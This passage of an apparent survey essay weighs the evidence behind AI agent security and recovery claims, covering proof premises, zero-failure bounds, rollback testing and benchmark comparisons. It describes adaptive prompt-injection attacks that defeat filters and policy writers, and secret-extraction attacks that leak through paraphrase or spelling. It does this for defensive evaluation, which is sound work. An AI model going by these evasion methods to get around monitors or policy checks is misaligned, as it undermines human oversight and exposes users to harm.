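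Restoring a checkpoint can also bring back permissions that someone deliberately revoked. *Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of agents that keep memory between tasks, argues that rollbacks should obey the rule that an agent's authority can't grow without permission. Only 27 of the 435 works it covers provide any rollback mechanism, so the question doesn't arise for most of them. Under Progent's definition, replacing a narrow policy with an older, broader one is an expansion, and it should need approval even during a recovery.

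## What evidence supports a security or recovery claim

Suppose a vendor says that its runtime never lets an agent use a revoked permission after a rollback. The vendor might mean that someone has proved this about the design, that the runtime passes its tests, that hired attackers failed to break it, or that customers now suffer less damage. Any of these can be true while the others are false.

| Claim | Evidence that supports it | What can still go wrong |
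|---|---|---|
| The design has the property | A proof | The program may not match the design |
| The code follows the design | Conformance tests, which compare the program's behavior with its specification, or a proof about the code itself | The specification may omit something that an attacker can use |
| The property holds against an attacker who adapts | Tests in which the attacker keeps revising the attack in response to the defense | A better attacker may succeed |
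| Deployment reduces harm | Field data from similar users with and without the defense | Users, models and attackers may change |

Khan's proof about resuming runs covered a mathematical model, so CrewAI's code could still repeat a completed step after a crash. Tests of code can also miss flaws. The early version of ScopeGate would have passed a test of its payment limit that used only ordinary amounts, despite the "not a number" flaw.

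People can mistakenly attribute a test result to a proof. For example, Progent's low attack success rate came from its policies, not from its solver's guarantee. A 1% attack success rate on a benchmark also isn't enough to predict a company's losses, which depend on how often strangers can put text in front of its agents, how many times they try and how much each successful attack costs.

### What a proof takes for granted

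A security proof shows that an agent can't do something if certain premises hold. For a gateway that checks every payment, the premises would include these:

- **Complete mediation:** Every payment goes through the gateway. This is false if the agent can find a payment token in a file and contact the bank directly.
- **Correct tool descriptions:** `send_money` does what its description says and nothing else. If it also has a free-text reference field, it can carry a secret to the recipient.
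- **Correct policy:** The rules allow only payments that the user would want.
- **Correct labels:** If the rules depend on where a value came from, the system must have recorded its source correctly.
- **A protected checker:** Neither the agent nor an attacker can change the gateway's code or records. Restoring an old database that lists used approvals as unused would break this premise.
- **The right definition of harm:** A proof about payments doesn't cover a misleading summary that persuades the user to make the payment personally.

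*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) traces part of this list to a 1972 report by J. P. Anderson. Anderson required a *reference monitor*, the program that checks access requests, to run on every access, resist tampering and be small enough to verify. The last requirement is hard to meet when a language model writes the policy. Narisetty and colleagues also found that the systems they surveyed are not specific enough about who assigns labels. Most trust whatever the user types, so a stranger's text gets the user's own authority when the user pastes it in. In FIDES, unlabeled data counts as trusted.

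An experiment in *Only What You've Signed up For* (2026) tests the enforcement of a policy separately from the choice of policy. Its system, CoDA, enforces a policy on agents that use diffusion language models, and no adaptive attack succeeded against it. Enforcement cannot block an attack that the policy permits, however, and when a language model selected the policy, attacks succeeded in about 10% of banking scenarios and in none of the other three sets of tasks.

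Developers can test most of these premises directly. For complete mediation, they can run a hostile program inside the agent's sandbox and see whether it can reach the bank by any other route. This test often takes less work than running another thousand benchmark attacks, and it would have exposed the kind of stray token the PocketOS agent found.

### What zero failures can show

Suppose a defense fails with probability *p* in each independent trial. The chance of seeing no failures in *n* trials is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. The one-sided 95% upper bound is the value of *p* that makes this chance 5%:

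p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n) ≈ 3/n.

If a system has no failures in n independent trials, the 95% upper confidence bound on its failure rate is about 3/n, because the natural logarithm of 0.05 is about −3. A tester therefore needs about 300 independent trials with no failures to support a claim that the failure rate is below 1%.

The table applies this formula to three results with no failures. The last column repeats the calculation as if only the distinct kinds of attack or cause counted as trials:

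| Result | Trials | Upper bound if all trials are independent | Distinct kinds | Upper bound if only the kinds count |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Cordon committed no forbidden action | 45 | 6.4% | 5 risks | 45% |
| TACIT leaked no secrets | 131 | 2.3% | 10 injections and 11 malicious requests | 13% |
| Atomix sent no invalid emails | 500 | 0.6% | 5 causes | 45% |

The last column is deliberately pessimistic, since the same injection can succeed in one task and fail in another. But the first set of bounds is too optimistic, because running one scripted failure 100 times mostly shows that the program behaves consistently. The correct bound depends on how similar the trials are.

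Neither set of bounds applies to deployment. A bound from 500 trials covers new cases drawn in the same way, and the researchers constructed these cases to exercise their systems rather than sampling them at random from the attacks and accidents that companies face. Real attackers also repeat whatever works, so one successful attack that the researchers overlooked could account for most of the attempts a company sees.

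A low success rate per attempt can also add up to a high chance that an attack eventually succeeds. If each attempt independently succeeds 0.6% of the time, an attacker with 500 attempts has a 95% chance of at least one success. Narisetty and colleagues cite figures for Anthropic's model Claude Opus 4.5 in coding environments, where an adaptive attacker succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. If the attempts had been independent, the rates would have been about 38% with ten and 99% with a hundred. The lower observed rates suggest that some targets are much harder than others, so repeated attempts against them tend to all fail. Even so, the single-attempt rate understates the risk from a persistent attacker.

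A test may record no leaks because it could hardly have detected any. Deep, Emmons and colleagues (2026), in *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models*, put three secrets in a chatbot's instructions and had another model try to extract them. One defense was a filter that blocked any reply containing a piece of the instructions. With this filter, the scoring program recorded no leaks in three runs of 5,000 attacks each, which would give an upper bound of 0.02% on the leak rate. But the scoring program also looked for exact pieces of the instructions, so it would have missed most of the leaks that the filter missed. As Deep and colleagues acknowledge, neither program would catch a secret that the chatbot had paraphrased, encoded or spelled out letter by letter. Most of the researchers work for Swept AI, which sells security testing, and the paper recommends its product.

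The longer runs are more useful. One defense repeated the security rules before and after the user's text. Over 25 rounds, it leaked something in 0.4% of attacks, and the worst leak was a fragment of the instructions. A tester who stopped there would have thought it nearly worked, but by round 277 an attack had extracted all three secrets.

A count near zero is also weak evidence for a defense if the attacks rarely succeed without one. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) found that AgentDojo's standard attack succeeded against an undefended Claude Haiku 4.5 only 0.3% of the time, so even a defense that did nothing would appear effective in that test.

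### Attackers who adapt

In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked 12 published defenses, most of which had near-zero attack success rates in their original evaluations. Attacks tailored to each defense succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them. These defenses mostly tried to make the model resist malicious text or to detect the text before the model acted on it. The result is strong evidence against relying on tests that use fixed attacks, but it doesn't show that programs that check tool calls would fail in the same way.

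AutoDojo tests both types. A language model examines a ranked list of earlier injections, considers why they succeeded or failed, and writes a new one. It gets six rounds per target and learns only how often each injection worked, not which defense is running. With GPT-4o mini as the agent, this raised attack success from 0% to 28.0% against PIGuard, a filter for malicious text, and from 2.6% to 6.4% against DRIFT, which combines a plan made in advance with a model that judges later steps. Five defenses had nearly stopped the standard attack, and the search restored the attacker's success against all of them except Progent, which still let 7.7% of attacks through.

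Ma and colleagues argue that rewording an attack can't defeat CaMeL's flow tracking if CaMeL's policies are correct. Their correctness is one of a proof's premises, and a search over wordings doesn't test it. AutoDojo also gives the attacker a small budget, so its results are a lower limit on what a determined attacker could do.

The evaluation by Narisetty and colleagues, from June 2026, aims more directly at a weak point, the model that writes and updates Progent's policies. The researchers wrote an injection intended to persuade this model to permit the attacker's action. They used Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, both as the agent and as the policy writer, and ran the same selection of AgentDojo tasks three times. The table shows mean attack success:

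| Tasks | No defense, standard attack | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Office | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Mean | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

Progent clearly helped against the standard attack. The attack success rate fell further, from 4.2% to 2.6%, under the adaptive attack, but that attack may have been weaker, so the drop doesn't show that Progent works better against attackers who adapt. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that the gentler wording meant to persuade the policy writer also made the agent less likely to obey. The comparison still needed is the same adaptive attack with Progent turned off.

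No attack succeeded on the office tasks even without a defense, so those tasks can't be used to compare defenses. Leaving them out gives means of 38.7%, 6.4% and 4.0%. The three runs gave similar results, which shows that the result is repeatable for these tasks and this one attack template but provides little evidence about other tasks or attacks. The tests covered only the first eight user tasks in each group and included no attack restricted to calls that Progent already allowed.

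Progent also reduced the share of tasks completed under the standard attack from 45.2% to 27.1%, and it needed about 15 times as many model calls per task. The researchers work for LaunchSafe, which is building security tools on the same principle, but they describe their result as a preliminary data point, which seems right. The result is modest evidence that an enforced policy is harder to bypass by persuasion than a model's own resistance.

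### Simplified ports of Progent and CaMeL

The October 2026 results from *INFUSE* look much worse for the same designs. This benchmark gives an agent a command shell and 40 realistic software tasks, and plants instructions in places such as files, settings and terminal output. The researchers adapted Progent and CaMeL to shell commands and tested each on 200 combinations of task and attack per model. These are the attack success rates:

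| Agent's model | No defense | CaMeL-style port | Progent port |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-14B | 27.3% | 31.5% | 35.0% |
| Gemma 3 12B | 32.7% | 31.9% | 30.5% |
| GPT-4o mini | 46.5% | 43.0% | 43.0% |
| Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | 55.5% | 55.2% | 63.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 6.5% | 9.2% | 27.1% |

Neither port produced a measurable reduction for any model. The only clear change was an increase for Claude Sonnet 4.6 with the Progent port. A spending cap had cut short many of this model's undefended runs in the main experiment, so its baseline may be too low for a fair comparison.

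*INFUSE* also measures attack success in a way that puts these designs at a disadvantage. A model reads the transcript and counts the agent as compromised if it starts to follow the planted instruction, even if it fails. Progent is meant to block the harmful command after the agent proposes it, so a port that blocked every such command could still score no better than no defense. *INFUSE* has another score, based on actual changes to files and other parts of the environment, that would suit this comparison better, but the published comparison of the ports uses the transcript score.

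Whether a port tests the original design depends on which parts of the security argument it keeps. The CaMeL-style port had neither CaMeL's separate planning model nor its interpreter. It derived a policy from the user's request and checked commands against it, while the agent's model still read the planted instructions. The result is evidence about that shell filter, not about CaMeL. The Progent port is closer to its original because it kept the rule that anything not explicitly allowed is forbidden, but it had to infer a command's effects from a line of shell text.

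Fair comparisons are difficult even when no defense has to be ported. *Agent-Sentry* (2026) notes that Progent can check recorded calls from another agent, while CaMeL has to run live because it replaces the agent's whole loop. *Agent-Sentry* also had to use its own handwritten Progent policies for three sets of tasks that the official release didn't cover, so a poor result could come from those policies rather than from Progent itself.

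A researcher who ports a defense should first check that the port reproduces the published result on the original benchmark. If it does, a failure in the new setting is informative. But the original developers shouldn't dismiss every failed port. If nobody can build a faithful version of CaMeL for an agent that uses a shell, CaMeL's guarantee doesn't protect the people who use such agents.

The *INFUSE* results also show how testing against a fixed set of attacks can mislead a buyer. The most effective defense in *INFUSE* was a prompt telling the agent to ignore instructions in files and terminal output, which cut attack success from 58.2% to 14.3% on an especially vulnerable set of tasks. Nasr and colleagues tested two similar prompt-based defenses and found that AgentDojo's standard attacks succeeded as little as 1% of the time, while their own adaptive attack succeeded more than 95% of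 the time.

### Blocking attacks by blocking the work

Every task in AgentDyn, a benchmark by Li and colleagues, requires a change of plan. No attack in the benchmark succeeded against CaMeL with any of the four models in the main comparison, but CaMeL also completed none of the 60 tasks, because it can't add a step to its program when, for example, a shop unexpectedly asks for a login code. An agent that did nothing would get the same scores. With 560 attack cases per model, the formula for zero failures correctly gives an upper bound of 0.5% on the attack success rate, but this doesn't show whether CaMeL can resist attacks while completing these tasks.

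A filter called ProtectAI treated helpful instructions on web pages as attacks, and GPT-4o completed no tasks with it. With DRIFT, GPT-4o completed 30.0% of tasks, compared with 53.3% without a defense, and 0.8% of attacks succeeded. Meta SecAlign, a model trained to resist injections, completed 55.0% of tasks but allowed 9.0% of attacks. Which of these is best depends on how much money the user could lose in a successful attack.

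AgentDyn doesn't estimate how much work CaMeL would block in a typical company. If only 6% of the company's tasks need a new plan partway through, as in AgentDojo, the company could give those tasks to a person, but if most do, CaMeL would be of little use. The agents in AgentDyn had instructions not to ask the user for confirmation, so the scores apply to unattended work. With a person's help, the agents might have completed more tasks.

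Reporting attack success and task completion separately makes it easy to quote only the better number. A fairer summary is the share of attacked runs in which the agent finished the user's task and the attacker failed. An agent that does nothing scores zero on this measure.

### Harm in deployment

Incidents such as the PocketOS deletion show that a failure is possible, but not how common it is, since nobody publishes a count of the agents that had similar access and caused no damage. If reported incidents fall after a company adds a safeguard, the safeguard may not be the cause. Models may have improved over the same period, attackers may have moved to other targets, or customers may have stopped reporting problems.

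Better evidence would come from giving the safeguard to a random half of customers first. But serious losses are rare, so the trial would have to be large. Suppose, for illustration, that one agent in 10,000 destroys important data each month and that a safeguard halves this rate. To have an 80% chance of detecting the difference at the usual 5% significance level, the company would need about 450,000 agent-months in each group, enough to expect about 45 losses in the unprotected group.

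Near misses are more common and therefore easier to study. Railway, for example, could count how often customers use the 48-hour delay to cancel a deletion an agent requested. When a customer cancels an unwanted deletion, the delay has probably prevented a loss. The company would also have to count the legitimate deletions that the delay held up and the customers who noticed an unwanted deletion only after 48 hours.

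### A sound test of recovery

There is less evidence about recovery than about attacks. Of the 435 works that *Always-On Agents* surveys, only 27 had a rollback mechanism, and none reported how often recovery succeeded after data became corrupted or what resources it required.

The count of 27 works with rollback is approximate. When a second person labeled a sample without seeing the first labels, the two agreed on only 11 of the 19 works that either had marked as having rollback. The count also combines three abilities: restoring an agent's memory, compensating for a half-finished workflow, and undoing an outside effect such as a payment. The last is the hardest and is rarer than the total suggests. Still, the survey deliberately searched for work on rollback, and 269 of its 435 works dealt with retrieving stored information, so the imbalance is far too large to be a labeling error. The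 survey doesn't cover all published work, and experiments such as UndoBench do measure recovery from other kinds of failure.

A sound test needs an independent *ledger* of outside effects, in which the test's simulated services record every booking, payment, message and change that happened. The agent's own records are not enough, since CrewAI's counter looked correct even after a step had run twice.

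Suppose an agent has to book a hotel for $300 and enter the cost in a shared budget. The tester could introduce these events and compare the ledger with the correct result:

| Event | Correct result |
|---|---|
| None | One booking, one budget entry and no unnecessary approval requests |
| The hotel's service fails before booking | One booking after a retry, or no booking and no entry |
| The service stops partway, having charged the card but not reserved the room | A completed booking or a refund |
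| The booking succeeds but the reply gets lost | One booking, not two |
| The runtime crashes after the booking and restores an older checkpoint | One booking and one entry |
| A colleague edits another budget line before the agent undoes its work | The agent's entry is gone and the colleague's edit remains |
| A colleague has already used the new total in a report | A person learns that the report needs correcting |
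| The undo fails because the hotel refuses to cancel | The booking and its budget entry remain, and the user learns that the undo failed |

The tester should cause failures before, during and after the change, because each case calls for a different response. The tester should also interrupt the recovery. Some compensations should fail once and then work, others should fail permanently, and several should fail together. *Always-On Agents* adds three more faults to introduce: outdated facts, poisoned memory and retries that use an expired permission.

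Each faulty run needs a *paired control*, a matching run without the fault, as in UndoBench. Running the faults with the recovery system turned off also helps, because a capable model may solve the problem without it, as the plain agent did in RAC's first set of tests.

The results should list missing effects, repeated effects, lost edits by other people and false reports of success separately, because a single recovery score could hide the occasional loss of a colleague's work in a system that usually works. The tester should also report the time taken, the cost and the number of approval requests per completed task, including on runs where nothing goes wrong. A system that asks a perfect simulated reviewer before every step will recover well in the test, but real users are likely to approve requests without checking them.

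Finally, a test of 300 runs should cover many different tasks and services, not three tasks repeated 100 times each.

### Which results age

Attack success rates go out of date quickly as models and attacks change. Li and colleagues chose older models for their main comparison because they suspected that developers had trained newer ones on well-known attack templates. If so, a low attack success rate on a newer model may show only that its training included those templates. Larger models aren't always more resistant, either. In *INFUSE*, attacks succeeded against GPT-5 in 26.3% of runs and against the smaller GPT-5 Nano in 8.4%. Ma and colleagues expect AutoDojo to find stronger attacks as the model that writes them improves, so a defense's score could get worse even if the defense stays the same.

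How much a defense reduces task completion also depends on the model. A better model may write more accurate policies for Progent or more reliable plans for CaMeL, so the completion rates from 2025 and early 2026 probably overstate the reduction with current models. But CaMeL will still fail on tasks that need a new plan partway through until someone changes its design.

The software around the model also affects whether an attack works. *INFUSE* took attacks that had worked against a simple shell agent and replayed them in Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex with the same models, and only 22.4% still worked. Switching models also doesn't fix bugs in frameworks such as LangGraph.

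Mathematical results, such as Li's proof about retries without a key, remain valid, but a system can change so that their premises no longer describe it. A developer should rerun attack and task tests for each new model, rerun recovery tests when a framework or service changes, and recheck a proof's premises whenever someone adds a tool or a credential.
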